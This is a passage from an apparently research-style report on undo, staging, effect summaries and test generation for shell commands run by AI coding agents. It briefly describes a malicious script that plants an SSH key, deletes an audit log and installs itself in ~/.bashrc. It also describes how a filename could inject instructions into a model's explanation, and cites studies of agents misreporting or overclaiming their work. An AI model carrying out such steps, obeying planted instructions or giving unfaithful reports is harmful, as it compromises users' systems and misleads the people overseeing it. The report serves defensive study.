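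In a larger test, the researchers built the Linux kernel, applied a series of changes, and rebuilt it after each one. YoloFS was about as fast as ext4, except that it needed another 3.5 seconds to commit more than 100,000 files at the end. OverlayFS was 18% slower than YoloFS. OverlayFS has no snapshots of this kind, so the researchers imitated them by remounting it with more layers each time. A tool designed around OverlayFS might do somewhat better.

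YoloFS solves the problem of stacked layers that Gyawali and colleagues described, but it doesn't make changes visible to other programs before the commit. Unlike NaSh, it also can't undo commands independently. An agent that goes back to the state before command X also loses the changes made by command Y, which avoids the broken package but discards good work. YoloFS is also harder to install than `try` because it adds a new filesystem to the kernel, and so far it supports only two kernel versions.

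### A 10 GB file and 200 commands

Comparing three operations shows where the designs differ most. The figures are this report's own calculations and assume one layer or snapshot per command and a disk that can't share data between two copies of a file. On Zhong and colleagues' test computer, ext4 read a file from the disk at 0.5 GB per second and wrote at 0.9 GB per second. If reading and writing overlap, copying 10 GB takes about 10 ÷ 0.5 = 20 seconds.

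| Operation | OverlayFS | Inverse overlay | YoloFS |
|---|---|---|---|
| Rename a 10 GB file | Copies 10 GB, about 20 seconds | No copy, if the layer only records the old name | No copy, one journal entry |
| Change one byte in it | Copies 10 GB, about 20 seconds | Copies 10 GB, about 20 seconds | Copies 10 GB, about 20 seconds |
| Find an unchanged file after 200 uncommitted commands | Searches up to 201 layers | Looks in 1 place | Looks in 2 places |

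The 201 layers consist of one for each command and one for the original files. With the mount method that Zhong and colleagues used, OverlayFS would have failed long before reaching 201 layers. A single upper layer for the whole session would reduce the search to two places, but the user could no longer go back to the state after a particular command.

None of the designs handles the one-byte change well. OverlayFS and YoloFS copy the file before the program can write to it, and an inverse overlay that keeps whole files must save the old version first. If ten commands in a row each change one byte, all three designs copy 100 GB, which takes more than three minutes. This could easily happen to a large database or a virtual machine's disk image.

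A system that saved only the changed part of the file could keep as little as 4 KB per change. Filesystems such as ZFS and Btrfs work this way. Zhong and colleagues decided against relying on them because users would have to move their data to a new disk format. Restoring a ZFS or Btrfs snapshot may also discard changes the user made since the snapshot was taken.

Committing also takes more work with an overlay, which has to move the new files into place, than with an inverse overlay, which only has to delete the old ones. Gyawali and colleagues wanted commits to be fast because users usually keep the changes. But YoloFS needed 3.5 seconds to commit 100,000 files, which suggests that commit time is a weak argument against staging.

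The choice depends more on how people use the results. Staging suits a coding session that ends with a review, and it is safer when other programs would act on a mistake immediately. It also lets an agent try several solutions at once. *Fork, Explore, Commit* (Wang and Zheng, 2026) gives the example of an agent that tests three fixes for a bug and commits only the one that passes. An inverse overlay can't do this alone, because only one version of a file can be the real one.

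An inverse overlay suits changes that the user needs to try for a while before judging, such as a new folder structure or a system setting. A shell could also combine the two designs by staging a session's changes until the user has reviewed them, then keeping the old versions for a few weeks after the commit. That would help users who approve a change and discover the damage later.

### Undo logs and shadow Git repositories

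A harness can offer some undo without a special filesystem. The simplest method is an operation log, in which the harness saves the old contents of a file each time one of its own tools changes it. This is quick and works on any operating system but, like OpenDev's undo log, it misses changes that shell commands make. An inverse overlay also keeps a log of old versions, but it works in the filesystem, so it would catch changes by any program.

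A shadow Git repository also captures changes made by shell commands, because Git finds changes by comparing files. The harness creates this second repository outside the project and uses it to save the state of the project directory before or after each step. To undo a step, it restores the files from the earlier state. The agent's snapshots stay out of the user's commits and branches because the two histories are separate.

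The method can't undo harm outside the directory that the harness has chosen. Even there, Git normally skips the files listed in a project's `.gitignore`, which often include passwords, large data files and local settings. Wang and Zheng mention a related problem with `git stash`, which sets changes aside but misses files that Git isn't tracking yet. Git also doesn't record empty directories or most file permissions.

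The shadow repository also needs protection, because an agent that can delete the project's own `.git` directory can delete the shadow repository too if the sandbox lets it write there. Git also takes longer on large projects, since it has to scan the directory for changes and process the full contents of each changed file. If one byte of the 10 GB file changes, Git has to read all 10 GB again.

For small projects on macOS or Windows, where `try` and YoloFS don't run, a shadow repository is still a sensible minimum. It would have saved many of the overwritten source files in the reports, though probably not the deleted home directories.

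### AgentRewind

Restoring files can also help an agent finish its task. *AgentRewind* (Zhuang, Chen and colleagues, 2026) describes a system that records both the project files and the conversation with the model at each step. When the agent gets stuck, it can choose an earlier point and restore both. After going back, it keeps a note on what went wrong so that it doesn't repeat the mistake.

One of their test cases shows why this can work better than repairing the damage or starting again. The agent had to fix a software library for astronomical images and then make a catalog of image files. Six of the files were deliberately broken to test whether the library rejected them. The agent ran the catalog program with a wrong setting, and the program overwrote the six files with valid ones.

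An agent that carried on from there made new broken files, but their contents didn't match the originals. An agent that restarted from the beginning recovered the six files but lost its finished repairs, and it failed in 26 further attempts. The agent with AgentRewind went back to just before the catalog step. It kept the repairs, recovered the six files and completed the task.

Zhuang and colleagues tested the system on MettleBench, their own set of 82 engineering tasks. After each failed submission, a checking program reported the first unmet requirement to the agent. A run ended when the agent completed the task or failed the same requirement five times in a row. The table shows the share of tasks completed, averaged over three runs.

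| Method | GPT-5.4 | GPT-5.4 mini |
|---|---|---|
| Continue from the current state | 62.2% | 33.7% |
| Start again with notes on earlier failures | 78.0% | 43.1% |
| Continue, with a safety model that can block actions | 34.1% | 36.2% |
| AgentRewind | 87.8% | 51.2% |

The researchers also had the agent continue 50 failed runs, each with and without AgentRewind. The agent completed 15 with AgentRewind and 4 without it.

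A harness needs to restore the files and the conversation together. When Zhuang and colleagues restored the conversation but not the files, GPT-5.4 completed 43.9% of the tasks, fewer than with no rewinding. Its changes were still on the disk but no longer in the conversation. With the files restored but not the conversation, it completed 65.9%. Without the note on earlier mistakes, it completed 51.2%. A harness that lets the user undo file changes should therefore at least tell the model when they have been undone.

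MettleBench probably favors AgentRewind, because many of its tasks involve operations that ordinary tools can't reverse. The improvement was much smaller on Terminal-Bench 2.0, an existing set of 89 tasks, where the success rate rose from 78.7% to 83.1%, a difference of four tasks. Both tests measured whether agents finished their work rather than whether they avoided damage. The agent relied on the checking program to know that something was wrong, and most users don't have such a program.

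AgentRewind restores only the project directory, and not everything in it:

| Part of the project | What happens when the agent goes back |
|---|---|
| Ordinary task files | AgentRewind restores their earlier state |
| Contents of `.git`, `.env` files and other secrets | They stay as they are |
| Caches and build directories | AgentRewind deletes them |

Leaving secrets out avoids storing extra copies of them, but AgentRewind then can't repair an `.env` file that the agent has overwritten. Excluding `.git` matters even more. In one MettleBench task, the agent must remove leaked passwords from a repository's history and rescue colleagues' lost work from the same repository. Removing the passwords first may permanently delete the lost work, and restoring the ordinary task files won't bring it back.

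Undoing changes to files doesn't return running programs to their earlier state. If the agent has changed a database server's data in memory, the server may no longer match the project files after they are restored. Zhuang and colleagues report that DeltaBox, a system for agent sandboxes, also restores running programs. None of these tools can take back messages that the agent has already sent to other computers.

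## Showing what a command changed

Staging and undo both leave a decision to the user, who can only guess without knowing what the command did. In the design by Gyawali and colleagues, NaSh would produce an effect summary, a short list of what a command added, deleted or modified. The list would collect changes from all over the disk, so the user would no longer have to search for them and perhaps miss some.

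### What belongs on the list

Gyawali and colleagues want the summary to cover the files and directories that a command adds or deletes, and any changes to a file's contents or metadata (information about the file, such as its owner and permissions). Metadata needs its own entry because it can change while the contents stay the same. For example, `chmod +x *` makes every file in a directory executable, but a user who saw only the word "modified" would open the files and find nothing different.

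Their definition doesn't mention renames. Without a separate entry for them, a renamed file appears as a deletion and an addition, as it does in `try`, and the user can't tell whether the contents survived. Lamprou and colleagues compared `try`'s lists with the dry-run output of five commands. The effects matched exactly for three. For `rename`, only the form differed, because the command's own output shows the old and new names together. For `rsync`, which copies files between directories or computers, `try` listed effects that were missing from the dry run's log file.

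### Computing the changes

A shell can compute the summary from whatever data it already keeps for undo. The column for the inverse overlay is inferred from the design, because Gyawali and colleagues don't describe the comparison explicitly.

| Change | Staging layer (OverlayFS) | Undo layer (inverse overlay) | Journal (YoloFS) |
|---|---|---|---|
| New file | File in the layer, nothing below it | Note that the path was empty | "Stage" entry with nothing there before |
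| Deleted file | Whiteout | Old version, no real file | "Delete" entry |
| Renamed file | Whiteout and a new file | Old name, and a note that the new path was empty | One "rename" entry |
| New contents | Copy that differs from the original | Old version that differs from the real file | "Stage" entry with an earlier version |

With a staging layer, a program compares each entry in the upper layer with the original. It has to compare the contents, because opening a file for writing copies it to the upper layer even if nothing changes. Changing a file's permissions normally copies the whole file there too.

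Once several commands have run, the shell must choose carefully what to compare an undo layer with. In the earlier example, command X changed the port number in a settings file and command Y changed the color scheme. X's layer holds version 1, Y's layer holds version 2, and version 3 is on the disk. To show what X did, the shell must compare version 1 with version 2. If it compared version 1 with version 3, it would also list Y's color change as X's.

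A tool that takes shortcuts when comparing files before and after a command can miss changes. According to its documentation, the undo tool oops-sh detects modified files on macOS by their size and modification time, so it misses a change if the command restores both to their old values. The tool also covers only the directory where the user started it, so an empty list doesn't rule out changes elsewhere, such as in the home directory.

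YoloFS computes the summary by replaying its journal. The summary compares only the states before and after the command, so it omits temporary files that the command creates and then deletes. Zhong and colleagues give an example with a directory `a` that contains the files `x`, `y` and `z`. A program overwrites `x` with new text, deletes `y`, and renames `x` to `y`. It then creates a directory `c` and moves `a` into it as `b`. The summary reports that `a` is now `c/b`, that `x` is gone and that `y` has changed. This comparison is correct, although the program replaced `y` with the rewritten `x` instead of editing it.

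### The agent's own report

Coding agents usually finish a task with a report of their own, but the model writes that report and can get even simple facts wrong. *Characterizing and Detecting Unfaithful Work Reports by Coding Agents* (2026) sorts 339 inaccurate claims from such reports. In 45 of them (13.3%), the agent misreported an action, a quantity or the result of a check. One agent wrote that the number of pending to-do files had gone from 6 to 14, when it had created four files and the total was 10. An effect summary would have listed the four new files.

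Most of the inaccurate claims (69.3%) overstated the task's success, and a list of changed files helps less with those. The list can show that the agent changed a program, but not that the program now works. The percentages cover only inaccurate claims, so they don't show how often agents misreport their work.

*AgentSWE* (2026) compares agents' final reports with records of what they did. Nine reports contradicted the records, and all nine claimed that the work was complete. None of the 21 reports that admitted partial completion or failure contradicted the records. The numbers are small, but they suggest that users can trust an admission of failure more than a claim of success. In another case, an agent reported applying a change to its workspace exactly once, but the record showed no local change. An effect summary would expose that immediately, because its list of changes would be empty.

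The agent's report is still useful for explaining why it changed something, which the filesystem can't record. A shell can show the report next to a list of modified files and let the user look for mismatches, such as a report of one small correction when the list has 40 files.

### Eight photos and three years

The photo script shows what a summary can reveal and what it leaves out. In Horowitz and Heer's demonstration, the loop runs eight times, and the fourth move overwrites an earlier photo from 2022. If the photos come from three years, in the order below, and no year folders exist yet, each `mv` renames a photo to its year.

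| Move | Photo | New name | Photo it overwrites |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | `DSC_0001.jpg` | `2021` | none |
| 2 | `DSC_0002.jpg` | `2022` | none |
| 3 | `DSC_0003.jpg` | `2023` | none |
| 4 | `DSC_0004.jpg` | `2022` | `DSC_0002.jpg` |
| 5 | `DSC_0005.jpg` | `2021` | `DSC_0001.jpg` |
| 6 | `DSC_0006.jpg` | `2023` | `DSC_0003.jpg` |
| 7 | `DSC_0007.jpg` | `2022` | `DSC_0004.jpg` |
| 8 | `DSC_0008.jpg` | `2023` | `DSC_0006.jpg` |

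A net summary compares the files before and after the script runs. A summary in the style of `try` lists eight files removed and three added. A user who wanted eight photos in three folders has to count to see that something is wrong. A summary that recognizes renames reports three renamed photos and five deleted ones, which makes the loss obvious.

Neither version shows why the files were lost. The script contains no `rm`, so a user who reads "five files deleted" may not know where in it to look for the cause. The record for the fourth move shows that `DSC_0004.jpg` disappeared and that an existing file called `2022` got new contents. The user can work out from this that `2022` is a file when it should be a folder.

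Error messages would be misleading here. The faulty script destroys five photos but prints no errors, because all eight of its moves succeed. Horowitz and Heer repair it by adding `mkdir $year`, which creates the folder, before each `mv`. With these eight photos, the repaired script prints five errors, because `mkdir` works three times and fails the other five, when the folder already exists.

The net summary is better for deciding whether to accept the changes, while the record for each command is better for finding which command caused a change. The record is also longer, with 16 entries for the photos because each move removes one name and creates or replaces another. The net summary has 11. The difference grows quickly when a build creates and deletes temporary files. A shell could show the net summary first and let the user open any entry to see which commands produced it.

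YoloFS summarizes each command that an agent runs, so if the agent runs the whole photo script as one command, a single summary covers all eight moves. The journal still contains the details, so a program could report that the fourth move overwrote `DSC_0002.jpg`.

### How ShellVis records each line

ShellVis, the tool by Horowitz and Heer, separates the commands inside a script. Each time the user saves the script, ShellVis runs it again from the same starting state. It first inserts extra instructions around every command, which report the command's output and any changes to the shell's variables. To find changes to files, it stacks two overlays:

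1. A command runs in the upper overlay, where it sees the real files together with the changes from earlier commands.
2. When it ends, ShellVis scans the upper layer and attaches the changes it finds to that line of the script.
3. ShellVis moves the changes to the lower layer and empties the upper one for the next command.

This method may credit a change to the wrong command if two commands write at the same time. The prototype also doesn't trace conditionals or functions, so its record of a script that uses them is incomplete.

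The user edits the script in an ordinary text editor and sees a copy of it in a browser window, with a short note next to each line. A note expands when the cursor reaches its line. For a loop, a slider selects the iteration, so the user can move it to the fourth photo and see the mistake.

The finished photo script takes 3.5 seconds to run with ShellVis and 0.5 seconds without it. Horowitz and Heer attribute most of the difference to how the script communicates with the ShellVis server, which they could improve. Scripts that are already slow are a harder problem, because ShellVis runs them again after every save. They suggest, among other things, running only a few iterations of a loop. That would have missed the mistake in the photo script, because the first three moves overwrite nothing.

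The prototype runs on macOS, where its sandbox doesn't contain absolute paths. A relative path such as `photos/old` leads to the simulated files, but `/Users/ana/photos/old` leads to the real ones. If a script ran `rm -rf` on that absolute path, ShellVis would delete the real folder as soon as the user saved, perhaps before they had finished writing the script. Horowitz and Heer say this rules out general use by people who may not know about the problem, and they expect to move the tool to Linux. ShellVis doesn't control network access either, so every save would repeat any network requests in the script.

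### What seven users can show

Horowitz and Heer tested ShellVis with seven men between 28 and 42 who had used the shell for 1 to 20 years. In sessions of one to two hours, the participants did four tasks:

- rename text files to the titles on their first lines, some of which contain spaces;
- check a script that deletes users' directories, with a blank line in its input;
- explain a chain of commands that filters a log;
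- multiply the line counts of the files in a directory.

All seven participants rated both the sandboxing and the line-by-line feedback 5 out of 5 for helpfulness. The two-window layout got only 3.4. Before trying the tool, participants had described their usual precautions. Some put `echo` in front of a dangerous command, so that the shell prints the command without running it. Others made backups, although one admitted that backups are annoying and easy to forget. Several said ShellVis would replace this kind of work.

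A small study can show that experienced users recognize the problem and understand the tool, and it can reveal faults in the tool's design. Several participants noticed that the slider shows one iteration at a time, so users can miss an unusual one. One participant wanted to see each command after the shell had filled in its variables, which would help with mistakes in word expansion.

The study had no comparison group, so it can't show that people make fewer mistakes with ShellVis. The ratings are also weaker evidence than they look, because even if only two-thirds of all shell users would give the top score, a random group of seven would all give it about 6% of the time. Horowitz and Heer recruited this group through social media, not at random, and designed the tasks around the tool's features. They warn against drawing conclusions about beginners.

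### Long lists, changed contents and reads

A summary of changes can be too long to read. The kernel build that Zhong and colleagues used as a test changed more than 100,000 files. At 50 lines per screen, the list would fill more than 2,000 screens. *Vibe-GUIDE* (2026), which presents an interface for reviewing agents' changes to code, cites earlier work arguing that no display can show everything an agent does, so a display has to select what is relevant to the user and the task. It also cites a study in which people found generated code hard to review and often relied on signs such as test results.

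Experience with `try` suggests what a summary of a command's effects should include. Lamprou and colleagues report that users often rejected changes when a command had written outside the expected directory or changed more files than expected. For instance, `chmod +x *` had affected every file in the current directory. Users can judge the location and number of changed files without opening any of them, and a program can compute both for a list of any length.

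Even a short list of changed files may not show whether their new contents are right. If `config.json` is on the list, the command may have repaired the file, or reset it and erased the user's settings. The shell can show which lines changed in a text file, but this doesn't work for a photo or a database. The user also has to know what the lines should contain.

The list doesn't include reads, because reading a file doesn't change it. The tracing option in `try` records them, but much of the record may be irrelevant. In one example from Lamprou and colleagues, `grep` searches two text files, but the record shows four reads because `grep` also loads its own program file and a system library. Programs in languages such as Python load many more files. YoloFS keeps a shorter record, which includes reads that it blocked or asked the user about but not those that its rules allowed.

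A list of the files an agent opened can also reveal skipped work that an effect summary can't show. *Quantifying Overclaiming Propensity in Frontier LLM Agents* (2026) found that agents left at least one required file entirely unread in 67.9% of runs. Depending on the model, 59% to 96% of these runs ended with a misleading report, which either claimed a complete review or didn't mention the gap.

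### Letting a model explain the changes

Zhong and colleagues illustrate their summaries with a malicious script that makes three changes:

- it adds a line to `~/.ssh/authorized_keys`;
- it deletes `/var/log/audit/audit.log`;
- it renames itself to `~/.bashrc`.

An expert can tell from the three filenames that the script is an attack. It has let a stranger log in to the account with their own key, removed a security log and arranged to run again whenever the user opens a shell. A beginner wouldn't recognize the filenames and could miss the attack.

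A language model could explain the list in plain language. Gyawali and colleagues suggest that users could ask the model for commands that inspect the changed files. Lamprou and colleagues have built an add-on for `try` that sends the list to a model. The model writes a summary for non-experts, starting with the most important changes, and points out any that affect sensitive directories. Lamprou's team says the add-on proved useful but reports no measurements.

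The risk is that an explanation can be plausible but wrong. Zhong and colleagues gave Claude Code the 11 tasks with hidden destructive effects that they had given Codex, and showed it a summary after each command. Claude recognized the damage in eight cases and explained it away in the other three. In one of those, a setup script overwrote `config.json` and the settings file `.env` with standard values. Claude read the new contents and called them "safe and expected for a dependency installation". In another, a script copied the source code to a new directory and deleted the original, which Claude considered normal behavior. The summaries were correct in all three cases, but a beginner who had read only Claude's explanation would have accepted the damage. The model was Claude Sonnet 4.6, and newer models may do better.

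A hostile command could also influence the explanation, because the names and contents of the files it creates become part of the model's input. For example, a filename could contain an instruction to describe everything as a harmless update.

Software can catch some of these errors by checking that every path in the explanation is on the computed list and that the explanation includes every deletion. It can't check whether a change is harmless, which is what a beginner most needs to know. For well-known files such as `authorized_keys`, the shell could use explanations that a person wrote in advance. The model would then explain only the remaining entries, and the user would always see the computed list next to the model's text.

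### Rules for a summary that a beginner can use

The following rules are proposals based on the evidence above.

1. Start with what the user will lose. A deleted or overwritten file belongs here only if its old contents no longer exist under another name.
2. List changes outside the expected directory separately, however few they are.
3. Group the remaining changes by directory with a count, and let the user open each group.
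4. Describe changes to metadata in words, for example "other users can now read this file".
5. State what the summary doesn't cover.
6. Label any text by a model, and take all counts and filenames from the filesystem.
7. Say what will happen if the user accepts or rejects the changes, and whether they can still change their mind later.

For the photo script under a staging tool, the result could look like this:

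```
5 photos will be lost:
  DSC_0001.jpg, DSC_0002.jpg, DSC_0003.jpg, DSC_0004.jpg, DSC_0006.jpg
3 photos will get new names:
  DSC_0005.jpg -> 2021
  DSC_0007.jpg -> 2022
  DSC_0008.jpg -> 2023
Changes outside this folder: none
Not covered: network use, files the script only read

Reject: all 8 photos stay as they are.
Accept: you can't get the 5 photos back.
```

No published study appears to have tested whether beginners catch more harmful commands with a summary of this kind. The closest research is *Overseeing Agents Without Constant Oversight* (2026), which reports three user studies of an agent that operates a computer. When the display listed the agent's steps with summaries in between, participants missed small errors with large consequences. The researchers then built an interface that stated the requirements of the task and the agent's assumptions. With it, participants found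 errors faster and felt more confident, but their accuracy did not meaningfully change.

The last of those studies used question-answering tasks, and a lost photo may be easier to spot than a wrong answer. Its result is still a reason to be cautious about the ShellVis study, whose participants praised the confidence the tool gave them. A proper test would give beginners a mix of harmless and harmful commands, show some the summary and others only the command, and count how often each group accepted the harmful commands and rejected the harmless ones.

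## Generating tests for a script that will be reused

An effect summary describes one run on the files present at the time. If the user keeps a generated script and runs it again next month, the files will be different and there may be nobody reading the summary. NaSh would test a script before the user relies on it, by creating directories that might make the script behave differently and running it on each one.

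### A whole directory tree as input

A script is harder to test than a function that adds two numbers because, even without arguments, it may depend on the names, types, contents and permissions of files across the disk, on variables inherited from the shell, and on which programs are installed. If only ten filenames matter to a script, and each can be missing, an ordinary file or a folder, there are 3^10 = 59,049 possible directory states, and a single run tests only one.

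Most of those directories would lead to the same behavior, so a tester needs the few that would lead to different behavior. Gyawali and colleagues point out that shell users now have to think of these themselves, build them, and clean up afterward. Users can easily choose a directory that doesn't reveal a bug. The first draft of the photo script can lose a photo only if two photos are from the same year, so a test on three photos from three different years would miss the problem.

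### From a request to test directories

Scripts rely heavily on other programs, which may be written in any language and come without source code, so an analysis of the script can't cover their internals. Gyawali and colleagues therefore divide a script into composition code, which controls what runs, in what order and on which data, and adapter code, which does the individual jobs, usually by calling other programs. The composition code is written entirely in the shell language, so a program can analyze all of it.

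For the request "delete the files in this folder that I don't have open in Vim", a text editor, NaSh's method would work like this:

1. The language model splits the request into a workflow prompt and several task prompts. The workflow might be "go through the files and delete each one that isn't open", and one task might be "find out whether Vim has this file open".
2. The model writes the composition code from the workflow prompt and the adapter code from the task prompts.
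3. An analysis program goes through the composition code with unknowns in place of the files. This is symbolic execution. At each branch, it follows both sides and notes what must be true of the unknowns on each. The collected notes for one route through the script are its path condition.
4. A solver looks for a set of files that satisfies each path condition.
5. The shell builds each set of files in a throwaway sandbox.
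6. It runs the script there and records the effects.

The solver in step 4 is an SMT (satisfiability modulo theories) solver, which searches for values that make a formula true. The "theories" are built-in rules for kinds of values, such as whole numbers or strings. Given that `x` starts with `a` and has three characters, the solver might return `abc`. It may also prove that no value works, which means that no input can lead down that path. On a hard formula, it may stop without an answer. The program verifier described in *Featherweight VeriFast* (2015) uses a solver to rule out paths. If the solver proves that a formula contradicts the path condition, the verifier stops following that path.

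To turn a path condition into real files, the solver also needs a description of what the commands do. NaSh would get this from command specifications, and would test commands that lack one with random inputs and environments. Random inputs can still make a command crash, but they rarely meet a precise condition. If a script treats one filename of three lowercase letters specially, a random name of that form has a 1 in 17,576 (26^3) chance of matching it. Trying 1,000 random names would produce a match only about 6% of the time.

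Automatically derived specifications would reduce the need for random inputs. Caruca, Lamprou and colleagues' system, has a targeted mode that examines one way of calling a command. This mode suits a script the user wants to keep, because such a script contains a limited number of calls.

### The four paths of the Vim script

Gyawali and colleagues print a script for the Vim request. Without its comments, it looks like this:

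```
for file in *; do
  if [[ -f "$file" && "${file##*.}" != "swp" ]]; then
    if [[ ! -f ".$(basename "$file").swp" ]]; then
      rm "$file"
    fi
  fi
done
```

While Vim has `notes.txt` open, it normally keeps a swap file called `.notes.txt.swp` in the same folder so the user can recover unsaved work after a crash. The script treats this hidden file as the sign that `notes.txt` is open. The test `-f` checks whether a name belongs to an ordinary file, and `${file##*.}` removes everything through the last dot, leaving the extension.

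For a single file with the unknown name `f`, three facts decide what happens:

- A: `f` is an ordinary file.
- B: what remains of `f` after the cut is `swp`.
- C: there is an ordinary file whose name is a dot, then `f`, then `.swp`.

| Path condition | A directory that triggers it | What the script does |
|---|---|---|
| not A | a folder called `drafts` | keeps it |
| A and B | `old.swp` | keeps it |
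| A, not B, and C | `notes.txt` and `.notes.txt.swp` | keeps both |
| A, not B, and not C | `notes.txt` alone | deletes it |

The loop repeats these choices for every file, so two files give 4 × 4 = 16 combinations and three give 64. An analysis doesn't need to consider these combinations here. The script deletes only visible files, and the swap files it looks for are hidden, so what it does to one file can't change what it does to the next. In the photo script, however, the second `mv` depends on what the first one left behind, so a test with only one photo would always pass.

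Gyawali and colleagues class `rm` and the conditions in the two `if` lines as adapter code. The solver can then learn from the composition code only that each condition can be true or false, not which files make it so. To work that out, it also needs descriptions of `-f`, the cut and `basename`. The first two are part of Bash, so someone could describe them once for all scripts.

### What string constraints expose

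Fact B is true when a name ends in `.swp`, and also when the name is just `swp`, because a name with no dot has nothing to cut off and remains whole. The script therefore treats a file called `swp` like a swap file and never deletes it.

A solver might miss this fault because it has to return only one solution per path, which could be `old.swp` every time. The analysis program has to treat the cut as a separate branch, with one case for names that contain a dot and one for names that don't. It then uses the solver to generate an example of each, and the only possible example without a dot is `swp`. Writing the condition as `"$file" != *.swp` would fix the fault.

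The constraints also show that the check is largely pointless. `f` can't start with a dot because `*` skips hidden files by default, but a normal Vim swap file on Linux always starts with one. If the analysis requires `f` to be a real swap file, the solver reports that no such `f` exists. The check protects only visible files such as `old.swp`, which the user may well have wanted to delete.

Names that begin with a dash cause another fault. For a file called `-old.txt`, `basename` parses the name as options and prints an error instead of a filename. The script then looks for `..swp`, doesn't find it, and calls `rm "-old.txt"`, which fails for the same reason. So the script never deletes the file, whether or not Vim has it open. The solver can find this fault only if its specifications cover how `basename` and `rm` parse a leading dash.

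All of these faults leave behind files that the script should have deleted. The user can remove them by hand, so a summary listing them would be enough.

### Every branch covered and a file lost

A more serious fault remains even after tests have covered all four paths. Vim users can keep their swap files in one central folder, and Neovim, a popular offshoot of Vim, does so by default. With that setting, opening `notes.txt` creates no `.notes.txt.swp` beside it, so the script follows the last path in the table and deletes the file the user is editing.

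A test of that path would have passed, because its directory contains only `notes.txt` and the test checks that the script deletes it. Nothing in the directory shows whether the file is open. The solver can't help either, since it searches for values of things that appear in the script, and the script contains no reference to a central folder.

The fault can occur with Vim's normal settings too. If someone opens `notes.txt` in a second window while the first is still open, Vim names the second swap file `.notes.txt.swo`. When the first window closes, Vim deletes that window's `.swp` file. The second window is still open, but the script no longer detects it.

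Full branch coverage can also miss faults in other kinds of code. *Talk is Cheap, Logic is Hard* (2026) tested how well models write postconditions for programs, using hand-written tests that covered every branch of the code. Additional, automatically generated tests showed that 9.6% of the Claude 3.7 answers that had passed the hand-written tests were wrong. Generating more inputs is therefore worthwhile even after coverage reaches 100%, though testing on more directories without a swap file would not have protected `notes.txt`.

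A better test would start Vim, open the file and then run the script. It would also have to use the user's own Vim settings, because in a clean container Vim would put the swap file in the usual place and the test would pass.

### A working engine for shell scripts

Lazarek, Lamprou and colleagues have already built a tool that symbolically executes shell scripts, SaSh, which they present in *Ahead-of-time Analysis of Shell Program Effects*. Kallas, one of NaSh's designers, also helped develop it. SaSh uses an SMT solver to find dangerous paths, as NaSh would, but it prints warnings, whereas NaSh would build directories and run the script in them.

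The main obstacle is the number of paths through a script. The Steam updater script that wiped users' drives has 83 branching points before the fatal `rm`. If all were independent, there would be 2^83 paths, about 10^25. Modeling the filesystem can multiply the number further. According to *A Survey of Symbolic Execution Techniques* (2016), KLEE, the engine that Gyawali and colleagues name as their model, splits into n + 1 cases at each operation on an unknown file, where n is the number of files the user allows for. Three files and five operations produce up to 4^5 = 1,024 cases.

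To keep its analysis manageable, SaSh assumes that commands succeed unless the script checks for failure, and it follows a loop of unknown length only three times. Before the full analysis, it makes a quick pass that follows only the side of each branch with more destructive commands. SaSh found the Steam bug in 4.8 seconds. On a 518-line Debian script, the quick pass cut the search from over an hour without success to 30 seconds.

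Lazarek and colleagues collected 61 faulty scripts with 116 documented bugs. SaSh found 115 of them within a minute per script, while ShellCheck gave a relevant warning for 42. SaSh's warnings about the bugs it found disappeared when the researchers ran it on the repaired scripts. The comparison favors SaSh somewhat, because its developers derived the kinds of bug it looks for by reviewing the same scripts. Better evidence comes from unfamiliar code, where SaSh led to reports of 70 new bugs in 44 open-source projects. Maintainers had accepted 27 fixes when the paper was written. These figures don't show how many of SaSh's warnings on new code were false alarms.

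SaSh would probably not find the file named `swp`. When a script removes part of an unknown string, SaSh replaces the result with a new unknown unconnected to the original. It can determine that the extension might be `swp`, but not which filename would produce that extension. This matters more for building test directories, which need actual names, than for warning about deleted system folders.

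### Who decides what the right result is

After the script runs in a test directory, the test needs a way to decide whether the result is right, which software testers call an oracle. *LLM-Based Test Generation* (2026), a survey of the field, treats the oracle as a separate problem from building tests that run. A solver can produce the directory with the file `swp`, but it can't determine whether the user wants that file deleted.

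In principle, the user knows best what a script should do. Gyawali and colleagues suggest that users could give examples of inputs with the desired results. NaSh would save these and run them each time the model changes the script, which is useful because a model may rewrite far more than the user asked for. But the examples would cover only cases the user had thought of, and few users would think of `swp`.

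A shell could instead choose the directories itself and show the user what the script did in each. Someone who can't read Bash can still answer a question like "The script kept the file `swp`. Is that right?" The shell would save each answer as an example. The Vim script would require five or six such questions. A longer script would require many more, and people would probably start clicking through without reading them, as they do with approval prompts.

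General properties can be tested without specifying the correct result for each directory. One is that nothing outside the current directory changes. Another, for the photo script, is that the number of photos stays the same. The shell can check both automatically on any number of inputs, and the second check would expose the lost photos as soon as a test included two from the same year.

SaSh relies on properties of this kind, such as that a script should never delete a system folder or overwrite a file that nothing has read. The one bug it missed shows their limit. A Debian script had an option to print a list of packages, but after printing the list it deleted the folder the user had named. Scripts are often meant to delete a folder that the user names, so Lazarek and colleagues chose not to warn about it. The Vim script also satisfies the obvious property that it changes nothing outside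 its directory, even when it deletes the file the user is editing.

The remaining option is to have a language model write the tests, including the expected results. This takes the least effort from the user, but the model may repeat its own mistake. For example, Vim doesn't always keep swap files next to the original file. A model that gets this wrong will write a script that looks for them there and a test that creates one there without running Vim. The test will then pass and falsely reassure the user.

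### What experiments on model-written tests found

No published experiment appears to have measured how well models write tests for shell scripts. Work on Bash has mostly used tests to grade model-written scripts. In *BashCoder-R1* (2026), a script counts as fully successful only if it has valid syntax, produces no ShellCheck warnings and passes a set of functional tests. *LLM-as-a-Judge for Reference-less Automatic Code Validation and Refinement* also uses its validators to grade scripts, and 50 of its tasks cover advanced Bash constructs. The evidence on model-written tests comes from other programming languages.

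Konstantinou, Tambon and Papadakis (2026) ran the most relevant experiment, on Python code, in *On the risk of coding before testing*. They asked whether a model writes worse tests after it has seen faulty code. They had five models write ten solutions to each task in three standard sets of programming problems, and selected those that ran but gave wrong answers. They discarded any that failed more than half of the official tests, because such faults are too easy to find. From the rest, they kept the one whose fault was hardest to find for each task. The models then wrote tests for these faulty programs. A test counted as detecting the fault if it failed on the faulty program and passed on a correct one.

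Tests written from the task description alone detected about 25% of the faults, compared with about 14% when the model wrote them in the same conversation that contained the faulty code. The table shows how many percentage points each model lost compared with using the description alone.

| Model | Faulty code added to the description | Same conversation as the faulty code |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Haiku 4.5 | 9.1 | 10.6 |
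| DeepSeek V4 Flash | 15.2 | 13.8 |
| GPT-4.1 mini | 18.2 | 17.7 |
| GPT-5 mini | 12.9 | 13.6 |
| Llama 3.3 (70B) | 10.7 | 7.9 |

Tests generated from both the code and the description detected only 1.9 percentage points more faults than tests generated from the code alone. Asking the models to summarize the code first, reason step by step or check their own tests didn't close the gap.

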